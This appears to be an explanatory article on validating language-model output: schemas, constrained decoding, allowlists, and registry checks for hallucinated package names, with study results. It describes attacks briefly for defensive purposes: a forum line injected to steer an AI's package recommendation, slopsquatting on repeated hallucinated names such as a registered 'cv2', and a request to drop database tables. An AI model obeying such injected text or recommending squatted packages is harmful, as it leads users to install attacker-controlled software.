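# Output validation and allowlists for what AI systems recommend and read

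## What these controls are and where they sit

Output validation means checking what a language model produces before a person or program acts on it. An allowlist is a list of permitted items, and a system that uses one refuses everything else. Developers use both because language models name many software packages, web addresses, shops, phone numbers and sources that people then use without checking. Some of these are slightly wrong, some don't exist, and a few lead to a page or program that somebody planted in the hope that a model would send people to it.

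One reply from a coding assistant shows where the controls go. Suppose a programmer asks how to extract tables from PDF bank statements. The assistant recommends a Python package and gives a one-line install command, a link to the documentation, and a citation of a paper that supposedly found the package more accurate than its rivals. The programmer may well paste the command into a terminal without reading further. Or the assistant may run the command itself, in which case it is an agent, meaning a model that acts through tools, for example by opening pages or installing software.

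### From the sources to the action

Before the model wrote anything, it read the programmer's question, the developer's standing instructions and probably some material that the assistant had fetched, such as search results, a forum thread or project files. An operator can add a check at this stage by limiting which sites the assistant searches and which addresses it opens.

In the next stage, generation, the model composes the package's name piece by piece. It can consult a catalogue only if somebody has connected it to one. With retrieval grounding, software first looks up real entries, and the model answers from them. A stricter design lets the model choose only from an approved list.

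Most output validation happens after the text is finished and before it reaches the recipient. A program can extract the package name, link and citation from the reply and look each of them up. It would look up the package in a registry, the public catalogue from which people install software by name (PyPI for Python, npm for JavaScript). A lookup that establishes only that the name resolves to something is called an existence check. An authoritative-source check compares more of the output with the record kept by whoever has authority over the matter, such as a registry's entry for a package or a court's docket for a case.

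The last place for a control is just before the action, when the software around the model can still refuse an agent's request to run the install command. A person who runs the command in their own terminal has no such barrier unless their employer or operating system provides one.

Wherever it sits, a check can accept a bad item (false acceptance) or reject a good one (false rejection). When bad items are rare, most rejections can be false.

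### Four questions about one reply

A check on the programmer's reply might settle any of four questions. Is the output well formed? Does the thing it names exist? Is that the right thing? And is what the reply tells the reader about it true? Applied to the three items, they come out like this:

| | Install command | Link | Citation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Well formed? | The command parses and the name uses legal characters | The text parses as a web address | Authors, title and year are all present |
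| Exists? | The registry lists a package of that name | The domain resolves and the page loads | A catalogue holds a paper with that title |
| Right thing? | It is the PDF package described, from its real maintainers | The site belongs to the project | The paper is a credible kind of source for a claim about accuracy |
| True? | The package does extract tables from bank statements | The page documents the feature as described | The paper reports the result that the reply attributes to it |

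A yes in one row does not carry down to the next. The gap between form and existence is easiest to see with skills, the small bundles of instructions and files that an agent can download to learn a task. Yuan, Guo and colleagues (2026), in *Skills That Don't Exist*, sent 15,000 requests for skill recommendations to 12 configurations of models and agents. They required each reply in JSON, a standard format for structured data, with every name in lower-case words joined by hyphens. Names such as `file-system-operations` and `visual-studio-code` fit that format perfectly. No published skill had either name. These are hallucinated names: a package, skill, domain or citation that a model presents as real though none existed when the model generated it. (Models invent package names too, at rates that vary a good deal between models.)

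Whether a skill appears to exist depends on where one looks. Most of the configurations had a web-search tool, but a search for `visual-studio-code` returns many results about the popular editor, which don't show whether a skill of that name exists. Checking a neighbouring catalogue can mislead in the same way, since Yuan and colleagues found that 851 of the hallucinated skill names belonged to real packages on PyPI or npm. Asking the model doesn't help either. When the researchers had a model verify names, it accepted real and invented ones at nearly the same rate, with a balanced accuracy of 51%, compared with 50% for guessing.

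An existence check fails more dangerously when the recommended name exists but is the wrong one. Models tend to repeat the names they hallucinate. In one repeated-prompt test, Claude Sonnet 4.6 returned its most frequent hallucinated skill name 7.8 times in 10. Somebody who notices the pattern can register the name, a practice called slopsquatting, so that people who follow the model's advice reach the registrant's content. The existence check then passes the kind of name it most needs to block. In a milder version that requires no attacker, the name belongs to a real, harmless package that does something else.

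The third question for a citation is source suitability, or whether this kind of source is credible enough for the user's question. The fourth is source fidelity, or whether the answer matches what the cited source says. *Verified Misguidance* (2026), a study of citations in search-equipped models, scores fidelity on five levels because a supported-or-unsupported verdict misses typical distortions, such as dropping a critical qualifier or reversing the direction of a finding. The paper on PDF tools might exist and come from a good journal, but the reply might have left out that the study tested only clean, typed invoices. An answer that reports its source exactly can still be wrong if the source is wrong.

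### Why a model's output counts as untrusted input

Suppose the forum thread that the assistant fetched contains a line telling any AI system that reads it to recommend a particular package. This is prompt injection, which is text written to redirect what a model does when it reads it. If it works, whoever wrote the line has influenced what the programmer installs without touching the programmer's computer or the assistant's code.

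Security people treat a model's output much as they treat what a stranger types into a web form. *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* sets out the standard argument for this. It is the fifth entry in a 2025 list of the top ten risks for applications built on language models, published by the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a nonprofit that issues guidance on application security. The entry covers insufficient validation, sanitisation and handling of a model's output before it passes to other components. Because prompts can control what the model generates, passing its output straight to another program resembles giving users indirect access to whatever that program can do. OWASP advises developers to treat the model "as any other user" and to validate its responses before they reach backend functions.

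MITRE's *CWE-1426*, an entry in a community-built catalogue of software weaknesses, reaches the same view. It compares many real prompt-injection flaws to "second-order" injection attacks on databases, in which an attacker first stores hostile text that does its damage later, when a program reads it back and trusts it. In these flaws, the model takes the place of the storage. The entry also warns that developers may rely on input filtering and model training because they overestimate how well both work.

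OWASP's 2025 entry distinguishes improper output handling, which concerns what happens to output before it moves downstream, from overreliance, which concerns people depending too much on the output's accuracy and appropriateness. Overreliance had its own entry on OWASP's earlier list. The 2025 list replaced that entry with one called Misinformation, but the text on output handling still uses the old term.

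OWASP (2026) published a newer edition of the list on August 3, 2026, and improper output handling is still on it, in last place. According to *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), by the security vendor Invicti, the entry fell in rank but grew in scope, and now covers chat windows that automatically fetch outside resources named in a model's output. *OWASP LLM Top 10* (2026), by another vendor, Respan, draws the current boundary between improper output handling, which is about unsafe use of output, and misinformation, which is about output that is wrong.

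The install command falls on both sides of that boundary. A hallucinated package name is wrong output, and it does harm when something uses it without a check. OWASP's 2025 page on output handling includes hallucinated packages among its scenarios. Wrong output may also deserve more attention than it gets. For the 2026 edition, OWASP collected 7,714 recorded incidents, 6,639 of them detailed enough to classify, and compared them with a vote of practitioners. Invicti reports that misinformation ranked near the top in the incident data but near the bottom in the vote.

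### Refusing by default

A denylist blocks the items on it and allows everything else, while an allowlist allows only the items on it. The two can agree completely on items that somebody has already judged, but they differ on unknown ones. A package published this morning is on neither list yet, so a denylist allows it and an allowlist blocks it, whether it is malicious or excellent.

Computer security settled on denying access by default long before language models. In 1975, Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* listed "fail-safe defaults" as a design principle, meaning that a system should start from no access and define the conditions that permit it. They credited the idea to E. Glaser, who had suggested it in 1965. They argued that a mistake in a mechanism that grants permission tends to shut out a legitimate user, who soon notices, whereas a mistake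 in a mechanism that looks for reasons to refuse tends to let something in, which can go unnoticed through months of normal use.

The argument applies fairly well to model output, except that it depends on people finding out when they have been refused something. If an assistant silently drops the best package from its answer because the package isn't on the list, the programmer won't know there is anything to complain about.

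Saltzer and Schroeder also wanted every access checked, and they were suspicious of systems that save time by reusing the result of an earlier check. A package or domain that passed a check may have a different owner a few months later.

The same choice of default comes up when a check cannot finish, for example because the registry is down. A check that fails closed refuses the item, and one that fails open lets it through. The system in *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (2026) fails closed, so the agent's action does not go ahead if the rule engine hits an error. Failing closed reduces availability, because the agent cannot act while the checker is down.

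### An instruction in a prompt and a rule in code

A developer who wants a coding assistant to stick to approved packages can use the prompt to tell it to recommend only packages on a list and never invent a name. Alternatively, the developer can write a few lines of code that compare the package name in the reply with the list and reject it if it doesn't match. The two approaches can produce the same visible results for weeks.

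*From Alignment to Access Control* (Baracaldo, 2026) calls relying on the prompt to impose rules "Pretty Please" enforcement. Baracaldo, of IBM Research, attributes to it a well-known accident in which a coding agent deleted a production database after being clearly told to change nothing. An access rule outside the model that denied the agent permission to delete would have made those instructions far less important.

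Instructions help, but they do not prevent every failure. In *AgentPolicyForge* (2026), an agent running on Claude Sonnet 5 made forbidden tool calls in over 98% of the threatening test episodes when it had not been told the policy. With the policy in its prompt, the figure fell to 14.8% on one test set and 13.2% on the other. Putting a second model in front of the agent as a guard did not stop every violation either. Off-the-shelf guards let through between 10.5% and 16.6%, and one trained for the job let through about 8%. In the skill study, Yuan and colleagues told the models in two-thirds of the prompts to return an empty list if they were unsure and not to guess. A correct skill existed for every one of those prompts, but on average 29.4% of the distinct names the models returned were invented.

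A rule in code works differently because the model has no part in the decision. In the classic design that Baracaldo recommends, one component intercepts each action, another decides whether to allow it, and the rules are stored separately so their owner can change them without rewriting the application. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) goes further and treats the whole agent as an untrusted component that may attempt anything. Injected text may cause the model to request a forbidden package, but the string comparison that checks the request will still reject it.

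Such rules can be very small. *Reason Less, Verify More* (2026) uses short Python tests to check the arguments of an agent's tool calls and the state of the database. These tests can raise the share of tasks the agent completes, because the agent doesn't have to recover from bad writes that they block.

Code can only enforce requirements that someone has made exact. *ActPlane* (2026) examined the instruction files that developers write for agents in 64 popular software projects, and found that 74% of the material depended on context that no one could define in advance. "The package must be on this list" is exact, though the rule is only as good as the list, while "Cite a credible source" is too vague for code to check. For requirements that stay vague, Baracaldo accepts a model as the judge, while acknowledging that it will sometimes be wrong.

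## Checking the form of an answer before a program uses it

Form is the easiest part of an answer to define exactly, so it is usually the first thing developers check in code. Suppose the coding assistant passes its recommendation to an installer program instead of a person. The developer asks for four fields: `name` for the package, `registry` for the catalogue to search, `timeout_seconds` for how long the installer should wait, and `description` for a sentence to show the user. A schema is the written definition of those fields. It might require `name` to be text, `timeout_seconds` to be a whole number from 1 to 600, and `registry` to be one of three permitted values.

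Schema validation compares the model's reply with that definition. A parser first turns the text into data, a step that fails if a bracket or quotation mark is missing. A validator then reports any fields that are absent, of the wrong type, out of range or not among the permitted values. Anthropic's *Structured outputs*, a documentation page for developers using Claude, warns that these faults can occur even with careful prompting. If a reply is faulty, the program can reject it, repair it or ask the model again.

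Rejecting a malformed answer is the simplest response, but a strict parser also rejects good answers. In *Say What You Mean*, Kurt reparsed recorded answers from Llama-3-8B, a small open model, to a puzzle that asks for the last letters of four names. The model scored 35% with a strict text pattern. The same answers scored 61% with a handful of looser patterns, which also accepted replies such as "e-S-S-E" and "AAA R", so much of the apparent error was false rejection.

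Repair can be as simple as those looser patterns, or it can use a second model. Tam, Wu and colleagues (2024) found in *Let Me Speak Freely?* that 60% of Claude 3 Haiku's JSON answers to a set of maths word problems would not parse. Having a model reformat the broken outputs raised the scores. A repair can change the content as well as the punctuation, so the result needs validating again.

In a case study on the website of JSON Schema, the standard language for writing these definitions, a vendor argues that retrying until a reply is valid multiplies the bill, adds seconds or minutes, and may never succeed. The vendor sells the alternative, a way to prevent invalid replies.

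### How constrained decoding works

A language model writes in tokens, which are words or pieces of words. At each step it assigns a probability to every token it knows, and the software picks one. Constrained decoding removes the tokens that would break the required format before the software picks. As Geng, Cooper and colleagues (2025), in *JSONSchemaBench*, set it out, the procedure is a short loop:

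1. Software compiles the schema into a grammar, a set of rules that determines which tokens can legally follow any given piece of text.
2. The grammar takes in the text written so far and produces a mask, which marks every token as permitted or forbidden.
3. The model computes its probabilities as usual, and the mask sets the forbidden ones to zero.
4. The software rescales the remaining probabilities so that they add up to 1, picks a token, appends it and goes back to step 2 until the reply is complete.

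(Some systems compile the grammar as they go.) If *P*(*t*) is the model's own probability for token *t*, the new probability is:

*P′*(*t*) = *P*(*t*) / *Z* if *t* is permitted, and 0 if it is not

*Z* is the sum of *P* over all permitted tokens, which is the total probability the model assigned to them before masking.

Take the `registry` field, with PyPI, npm and RubyGems (the catalogue for the Ruby language) as its permitted values, and pretend that each is a single token. One programmer asks for a charting library without naming a language. Another asks for a Java library, which none of the three catalogues is meant for. The probabilities here are invented:

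| Next token | Charting library, before | Charting library, after | Java library, before | Java library, after |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| PyPI | 48% | 60% | 3% | 60% |
| npm | 24% | 30% | 1.5% | 30% |
| RubyGems | 8% | 10% | 0.5% | 10% |
| Anything else | 20% | 0% | 95% | 0% |

In the first case *Z* is 0.8, so 48% becomes 48%/0.8, or 60%. In the second case *Z* is 0.05, so 3% also becomes 60%. The installer receives a well-formed "PyPI" both times, and the second reply contains no sign that the model had put 95% of its probability on outputs that weren't allowed.

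Real values usually span several tokens, but the mask checks only the next one. Geng and colleagues give a toy example in which a model is about to write "89,000" in a field that takes plain digits. The mask blocks the comma, and the model, partway through a number it would have written with a comma, might produce "890000", which is valid but ten times too large.

### When no permitted value fits

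A field with a fixed set of permitted values is an allowlist built into generation. Its main strength is that a value off the list cannot appear. OpenAI advertises this for its own version of the feature, telling developers not to worry about a missing required key or an invented value. The weakness, as in the Java case, is that a required field has to contain something, so the model picks a wrong value when there is no right one. An ordinary allowlist can refuse everything.

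The usual remedy is to add a value such as "none of these" and have the program treat it as a refusal, for example by asking the user or passing the request to a person. This lets the model decline, but getting it to decline at the right times is harder.

Lee (2026), in *Repair, Not Improvement*, tested the effect of constraining output with a grammar on three very small models, of 0.6 to 4 billion parameters, that had to choose a tool for a user's request. Lee gave them each of 200 requests twice, once with the right tool among ten candidates and once with a list that lacked it, so that the correct answer was "None". The grammar permitted only the ten names and "None", and Lee ran every test in English and Korean. Compared with unconstrained output, the constraint made the models decline correctly less often in four of the six combinations of model and language, by up to 29.5 percentage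 points, and produced no clear improvement in the other two. The constraint had shifted the models towards naming a tool, as they also chose the right one more often in all six combinations when it was listed.

Lee ran a third condition that cut the answer off after one line without applying the grammar. Compared with that condition, the grammar turned 698 wrong answers into correct refusals. In 545 of these cases, the third condition had produced no readable answer. Lee concludes that the grammar repairs unreadable output but does not change the model's judgement.

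The share of probability that the mask removes, 1 minus *Z*, could serve as a warning. In an exploratory analysis, Lee found that this share strongly predicted the damage when it was above about 0.48, but did not predict it below that. In the invented example above, the charting request would fall below this threshold and the Java request would be far above it.

Models that answer questions about pictures can be far worse at declining. *Investigating Length Bias and Robustness in LVLMs for Multiple-Choice Question Answering* (2026) removed the correct option from questions about bird photographs and replaced it with "None of the above". When the options did not include the birds' names, Qwen2.5-VL-7B chose "None of the above" only 3.2% of the time.

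A model can also choose "Unknown" when a question has an answer. *LLM Abstention Can Be a Prompt Artifact, in Addition to Genuine Uncertainty* (2025) added "Unknown" as an option to true-or-false logic problems that all had an answer. DeepSeek-V4-Flash, which had solved 78.4% of them without the extra option, then chose "Unknown" for 42.4%. On easier multiple-choice questions, it chose "Unknown" for only 0.2%. Replacing "Unknown" with a synonym or a random word indicated that the presence of an extra option mattered more than its meaning.

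The wording of the instruction may help. *Penalty-Framed No-Valid-Option MCQA* (2026) distinguishes telling a model to abstain if it is unsure from telling it to abstain if none of the choices is correct. The second suits a permitted-value field better, because a model can be sure that nothing on the list fits. A developer still has to test both requests that have a right value and requests that don't, because testing only the first kind would have shown just the benefits of Lee's constraint.

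### Valid objects with false contents

An answer can match its schema and still contain a wrong value. In *The Constraint Tax* (Ray, 2026), a user asks for a 30-minute meeting with Leo. The model returns a calendar entry with the right date, time, attendee and topic, but a duration of 180 minutes. Every field has the right type, so a calendar program would accept the entry and block out three hours.

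Ray gave 200 such requests to Qwen2.5-1.5B, a model small enough to run on a phone or laptop. Every object was valid, whether the prompt only asked for the format or constrained decoding enforced it. But 91.5% were correct when the prompt asked for the format, compared with 48% under constrained decoding. In 102 of the 104 failures under constrained decoding, the only error was a wrong duration. Monitoring only the share of valid replies would not have revealed this drop in accuracy.

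Larger models put wrong values in valid objects too. In *The Structured Output Benchmark*, Singh, Khurdula and colleagues (2026) had 21 models extract facts from supplied text into a given schema. Most produced valid objects well over 90% of the time, but the best got 83.0% of individual values exactly right on ordinary text, 67.2% on text from scanned documents and 23.7% on meeting transcripts. The scoring is harsh, since "United States" counts as wrong where the answer key has "American". Some of the errors are inventions, though. One model listed a person's occupation as "American country music artist" when the source supported only "country music artist", a small addition that no validator would catch.

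A tighter schema catches some false values. If no meeting at the company runs longer than an hour, a maximum of 60 minutes would have stopped Leo's three-hour booking. It would not stop a 45-minute booking for a 30-minute request, because catching that error requires comparing the booking with what the user asked for.

### Preparing text for its destination

Some text is harmless as data and causes trouble only when another program reads it. Suppose the assistant fills the `description` field with this sentence:

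`Extracts <table> data from O'Neill Bank's statements`

Suppose a model's answer contains the name O'Neill and the phrase `<table> data`. It is ordinary text and passes the schema. If the developer pastes it straight into a web page, the browser treats `<table>` as an instruction to start a table, and the word disappears from the sentence. If the developer pastes it between single quotation marks in a database command, the apostrophe in O'Neill ends the text early and the command fails. In a command-line shell, the angle brackets mean "read from a file called table" and "write to a file called data". These errors are accidental, but someone who controls what the model writes can choose characters that do more damage.

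OWASP recommends treating output according to where it will go. For a web page, this means escaping the output, or replacing characters that have a special meaning with codes that display as those characters. The browser receives `&lt;table&gt;` and shows `<table>`. In case an escape is missing, OWASP also recommends a content security policy, a set of rules the site sends about which scripts the browser may run. Escaping for one destination doesn't protect another. An escaped web address can still lead to a bad site, and text made safe for a page may still break a database command.

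For databases, the standard protection is the parameterised query. The developer writes the command in advance with a placeholder, such as `INSERT INTO notes (text) VALUES (?)`, and sends the model's sentence separately. The database never treats the sentence as part of the command, so the apostrophe is stored as ordinary text. Placeholders work only for values, so table names need a list of permitted names instead. Placeholders also give no protection when the model writes the whole command. OWASP describes a chat feature that turns requests into database commands, where a user asks it to delete every table. The resulting command is well formed, but limiting the feature to a few prepared queries, or to an account that can only read, would stop it.

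The same approach works for actions. The developer fixes the command in code and lets the model supply only the arguments, instead of running whatever line the model writes. For the PDF package, the code would contain `pip install` and the model would supply the name. The program should check the name first, then pass it directly to the installer without a shell. For example, the check should require the name to start with a letter or digit, because the installer could treat a name that starts with a hyphen as an option that changes its behaviour.

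Model providers now do part of this checking. Anthropic's *Strict tool use* describes a setting that applies constrained decoding to the arguments of an agent's tool calls, so that they match the developer's schema. The setting controls only the form of an argument, which may still have come from a web page the agent had just read rather than from the user.

A fixed list of commands also limits which actions the model can trigger. In another of OWASP's scenarios, a general-purpose model passes its reply unchecked to an extension that also has administrative functions, and the extension shuts down for maintenance. An extension that accepted only the few commands meant for that model would have ignored the reply.

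### Which schemas the tools enforce, and how fast

Developers usually use an existing tool for constrained decoding, and these tools differ in how much of a schema they enforce. Geng and colleagues tested six of them in early 2025 on nearly 10,000 real schemas. Every tool produced compliant output for at least 86% of the short schemas for function calls. For long schemas with 100 to 500 fields, the best tool, the open-source Guidance, produced compliant output for 41%, and Outlines did so for 3%, mostly because it timed out.

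OpenAI's tool accepted only 9% of those long schemas, but its output complied with every schema it accepted. It failed closed, which at least shows the developer that there is a problem. By contrast, XGrammar, an open-source tool, refused to compile a schema in only three of the 45 categories in the official JSON Schema test suite, but in 38 it allowed at least one object that the schema forbids. A developer who assumes that XGrammar enforces every schema it accepts will often be wrong.

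These tools have changed since, but the big providers still support only part of the schema language. AWS, Amazon's cloud business, immediately returns an error when a schema uses an unsupported feature. Anthropic's Python software adapts the developer's schema before sending it, then validates the reply. Validating the reply is worthwhile with any provider, if only because a reply that hits its length limit can break off in the middle of an object.

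Measured delays vary even more. In tests by Geng and colleagues, a small Llama model took about 15 milliseconds per token with no constraint. Outlines and another tool, llama.cpp, doubled that to about 30. Guidance took only about 6, because it fills in tokens without running the model wherever the grammar leaves only one option. Outlines also spent about 3.5 seconds compiling each grammar before starting. *When Correct Isn't Usable* (2026) measured much larger slowdowns with small models on maths problems, which took 3.6 to 8.2 times as long as with an ordinary prompt. On AWS, compiling a new schema can take a few minutes. The service then keeps the grammar for 24 hours, so later requests run at nearly normal speed.

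### The dispute over format and reasoning

In 2024 Tam and colleagues reported that format restrictions harm reasoning, and that stricter ones generally harm it more. LLaMA 3 8B solved 75% of a set of maths word problems when it answered in plain text, 65% when the prompt asked for JSON, and 49% when the prompt also specified the fields. Parsing errors could not explain the gap. On the last-letters puzzle, the gap for the same model was 38 points, but only about 0.15% of its JSON answers failed to parse.

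Their data suggested that the order of the fields was one cause. On that puzzle, GPT-3.5 Turbo in JSON mode put the answer field before the reasoning field in every reply, so it gave its answer before working it out. The results were different for classification tasks. Gemini 1.5 Flash got much better at picking a diagnosis from 49 diseases when it had to answer in JSON, perhaps because the format limited it to the available choices.

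Later that year Kurt replied from .txt, a company that builds structured-generation software and so had a stake in the outcome. Kurt showed that the prompts in the comparison differed. One of the JSON prompts told the model to "use the tool" without naming a tool, mentioning JSON or listing the fields. With matched prompts and the same Llama model, Kurt found that structure helped slightly on all three disputed tasks, raising the last-letters score, for example, from 73% to 77%. Castillo, in *Structured outputs can hurt the performance of LLMs*, agreed that the original study had major flaws but still concluded that structured output can reduce performance. In 2025 Geng and colleagues ran four constrained-decoding tools on the same three tasks and sided with Kurt, finding that constraints left scores level or raised them by up to about four points.

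Researchers then separated the effect of asking for a format in the prompt from the effect of enforcing it during decoding, which early comparisons had mixed together. *The Format Tax* (Lee, D'Antoni and Berg-Kirkpatrick, 2026) found that, for six open models, asking for a format lowered scores by 3.9 points on average and enforcing it lowered them by another 1.6. Three recent closed models lost almost nothing when the prompt asked for a format, and often gained. Enforcement could still cause large losses in particular combinations. For example, GPT-5.4-nano lost 59 points on maths problems when a grammar forced it to answer in XML, an older data format.

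Nguyen, Silva and colleagues (2026), in *Constrained Decoding*, proved that masking cannot reduce the chance of a correct answer under certain conditions. The proof follows from the formula above. If the correct answer is permitted, none of its tokens is masked and each token's probability is divided by *Z*, which is at most 1, so the answer's total probability stays the same or rises. In their experiments with matched prompts, constraints matched or beat free generation. The largest gains, up to 17.4%, came from ruling out impossible answers, such as any answer to the last-letters puzzle that wasn't four letters long.

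Other results from 2026 point the opposite way. *Inference for Reasoning Models* (2026) found that asking for JSON made little difference to three models, while enforcing it lowered scores by 1.2 points on Qwen3-8B, 4.4 on gpt-oss-20b and 25.3 on Llama-3.1-8B. *Token-Oriented Object Notation vs JSON* (2026) reports that a very large model, Hermes-4-405B, fell from 92.5% to 35.0% under constraints that helped weaker models. In Ray's main test of small models, enforcement raised the share of valid replies from 61.5% to 100% but lowered the share of correct answers from 19.7% to 11.0%, although one of the three models improved. *Capacity, Not Format* (2026) describes a causal analysis that found no effect of format in 43 of 48 scenarios, but in the paper's own results, the same prompting technique left strong models unharmed and badly hurt weaker ones.

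The proof can be correct and the losses real, because the proof assumes that the model's reasoning stays fixed and that the grammar permits the correct answer in the exact form that counts as correct. A schema with room only for the answer gives a small model no space to write out its reasoning. A grammar that dictates spacing or field order may also block the form in which the model would have got the answer right. The original claim was therefore too broad, but a developer can't know without measuring whether enforcement makes a particular model less accurate.

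There is more agreement on the remedy, which is to let the model reason first and apply the format afterwards. Within a single object, that means putting the reasoning field before the answer field. *The Format Tax* recovered most of the lost accuracy by having the model answer freely, then reformat its answer in a second pass. The second pass nearly doubles the number of tokens. An earlier paper by Nguyen, Silva and colleagues (2026), *Thinking before constraining*, avoids this by having the model reason and format in a single pass. The model writes freely until it produces a trigger token, and then the software starts masking. In the group's later experiments, this added fewer than 15 tokens to a reply.

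## Checking software package names against a registry

A schema can require a package name to use legal characters, but checking whether a package with that name exists takes a registry lookup, which is a single web request. Most errors come from looking up the wrong name or inferring too much from the result.

### From a reply to a verdict

Churilov (2026), in *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, checked thousands of names that models had produced against the live PyPI and npm registries. A coding assistant could follow much the same steps before showing a reply:

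1. **Extract the names.** Software searches the reply for install commands such as `pip install pdfplumber` and parses the code for import statements. An import of part of a module, such as `os.path`, reduces to its first word.
2. **Normalise them.** PyPI treats `Flask_Login` and `flask-login` as the same name, so the check has to as well. On npm, a name such as `@opentelemetry/sdk-metrics` starts with a scope, a prefix that belongs to one owner, and the check should keep it whole.
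3. **Drop whatever can't be a registry package.** This covers modules that come with the language, such as Python's `os` and `json`, and names that the registry's own rules forbid.
4. **Query the registry.** Status code 200 means that the name exists, and 404 means that it doesn't. Any other response, such as a timeout or a server error, means unknown.

Churilov called a package name absent only if two separate lookup methods both returned 404, in two rounds at least 12 hours apart. A single 404 can mislead for a short time after a package first appears, because the registry's servers don't all update at once. An assistant can't wait 12 hours before answering a programmer, so its developer has to decide whether it allows or blocks names it can't confirm.

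Extracting package names from a model's reply is harder than it may seem. *Names Can Hurt* (Raj and Sahu, 2026) describes a checker built for small models that people run on their own computers. The checker's first version searched the whole reply, so it picked up `github` and `python` from ordinary sentences, as well as `np` and `pd`, programmers' abbreviations for two popular packages. When a tester typed "Install requests, flask and pandas.", the checker reported `and` as an invented package and didn't recognise `pandas.` because of the full stop.

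With that version, the model ran out of attempts without producing an acceptable reply on 79% of prompts. Reading only the code blocks, with a proper parser, cut this to 57%. A short table of import names helped reduce it to 30%. The prompt sets overlapped but weren't identical. Still, the drop is large, and the model hadn't become any better at naming packages.

### Why a naive check rejects `cv2`

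Python programmers install OpenCV, a widely used image-processing library, with `pip install opencv-python` and then write `import cv2` in their code. The install command names a package, while the import names a module, which is a unit of code inside the package. Python doesn't require the two names to match. A naive check that looks up the imported name on PyPI finds no package called `cv2` and rejects working code.

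Every import a checker rejects can be correct, because a module's import name may differ from its package's name on PyPI. Hillah, Richard and Hasnaoui (2026), in *Bayesian-Calibrated Detection of Hallucinated Package Imports in AI-Assisted Code*, collected 1,134 replies from six models to ordinary programming tasks. The only imported names missing from PyPI were `cv2` and `dateutil`, which each appeared 12 times. All 24 imports were correct, because the packages that provide these modules are called `opencv-python` and `python-dateutil`.

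The usual remedy is a table that maps import names to package names. Hillah and colleagues used a table with 15 entries, Raj and Sahu used one with 24, and Churilov used an existing one with about 1,157. No table is complete, because different packages can contain modules with the same name and rare mismatches never get added.

Checking the table first can also let a malicious package through. Suppose an attacker registers a package called `cv2`. The table maps `cv2` to OpenCV, so the checker would approve the name even when the reply contains the command `pip install cv2`, which would fetch the attacker's package. Raj and Sahu therefore consult the table only after PyPI returns 404, so a registered `cv2` would go on to further checks. However, this means the table can no longer clear a correct import once somebody else has registered the same name.

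Churilov's rule avoids that trade-off by tracking where each name came from. The table can clear a name that appears only in imports, but not one that appears in an install command, because the installer fetches whatever package has exactly that name. An assistant could also add the correct install command to its reply, so that a programmer who gets an import error doesn't have to guess the package name.

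### How often models invent package names

The standard baseline is Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues' *We Have a Package for You!* (2024). They had 16 models write 576,000 samples of Python and JavaScript code and checked the packages against registry lists from January 2024. On average, 5.2% of the packages from commercial models didn't exist, compared with 21.7% for open models. For GPT-4 Turbo, the best model, the figure was 3.59%.

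Many of the invented names recurred often enough for an attacker to exploit. The researchers took 500 prompts that had produced an invented name and ran each one ten more times. The same name appeared every time for 43% of the prompts and never reappeared for 39%. Only 13.4% of the invented names were within two characters of a real one, so most were not simple misspellings.

In April 2026, Churilov ran the same prompts on five newer models, with one reply per prompt, for a total of 199,840 replies. The figures here come from the paper's fourth version, published in November 2026. Earlier versions gave higher figures, which other pages still repeat.

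| Model | Invented names, as a share of package mentions | Replies with at least one invented name | Replies that declined or had no usable code |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 3.63% | 2.34% | 1.27% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 4.09% | 2.75% | 18.77% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 4.77% | 3.39% | 8.11% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 4.80% | 2.66% | 1.97% |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 5.02% | 2.15% | 31.51% |

GPT-5.4-mini ranks worst by mentions and best by replies, mainly because it gave no usable code for almost a third of the prompts. The differences between GPT-5.4-mini, Gemini and DeepSeek in the first column are not statistically significant. DeepSeek V3.2, the only open model, is no longer an outlier. All five models did worse in Python than in JavaScript, whereas in 2024 Python results were better on average.

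The best rate barely changed in two years, but the comparison is too loose to conclude that progress made no difference. Spracklen and colleagues collected package names from install commands and by asking the model which packages were needed, while Churilov used install commands and imports. The prompts have also been public since January 2025, so the newer models may have been trained on them, which would make their rates look better than they are.

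All five models invented the same 104 names, 88 of them for PyPI and 16 for npm. An attacker who registered one of these could reach users of models from four companies. Fifty-four of the names are one character away from the name of a registered package. Outsiders can't publish under four of the npm names, which are in a scope owned by the organisation behind Ember, a web framework. Reviewers at the security company Socket judged that anyone could register the other 12 npm names. Nobody has published a count of how many PyPI names on the corrected list are available.

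How often models invent package names depends heavily on the model and the request. In *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code*, Djire, Barr and colleagues (2026) asked eight small open models to list packages in four programming languages. The share of invented names ranged from 16.1% for Mistral 7B to 47.9% for the smallest Qwen model. Prompts that mentioned made-up packages raised the rate by up to 45 percentage points. But Hillah and colleagues found no invented imports on ordinary tasks once they had allowed for names like `cv2`. A check on everyday code may therefore produce few useful rejections, which will make its false rejections more noticeable.

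### The validator's own errors

Earlier versions of Churilov's paper compared names with registry lists from 2025 and treated import names as package names. The fourth version queried the live registries and corrected both faults, and every model's rate of invented names fell by about a fifth. For Claude Haiku 4.5, 296 of 1,394 apparently invented names were removed from the count. Of these, 189 were correct imports of real packages, 51 were names of packages that already existed when the model named them, and 44 were names that no registry would accept. The status of another 11 was unknown, and one was a spelling variant.

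Counting each name once gives a different picture. Across all five models, the earlier candidate list had 3,445 distinct names, and 2,282 survived the corrections:

| Reason for removing a name | Distinct names |
|---|---|
| Scraps of code or text, such as file paths and template placeholders | 696 |
| Breaks the registry's naming rules | 231 |
| The package already existed | 161 |
| Import name of a real package | 54 |
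| Status unknown | 21 |

Only 54 of the removed names were import names, but they caused the most false alarms when every mention is counted, because models use popular packages repeatedly. A developer who wants fewer false rejections should probably start with the import names that appear most often.

New packages appear every day, and a validator that relies on a saved list rejects them until somebody refreshes the list, as happened with the 161 existing packages. A live query avoids this but depends on the registry being up.

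Standard-library modules are another source of error. Djire and colleagues found that counting modules such as `os` and `math` as inventions raised their small models' invention rates for Python by up to 9.4 percentage points. Churilov checked for the same error and found no standard-library modules among the candidates. Both results can be right, because Djire's group asked for bare lists of packages, and small models may well put `json` on such a list.

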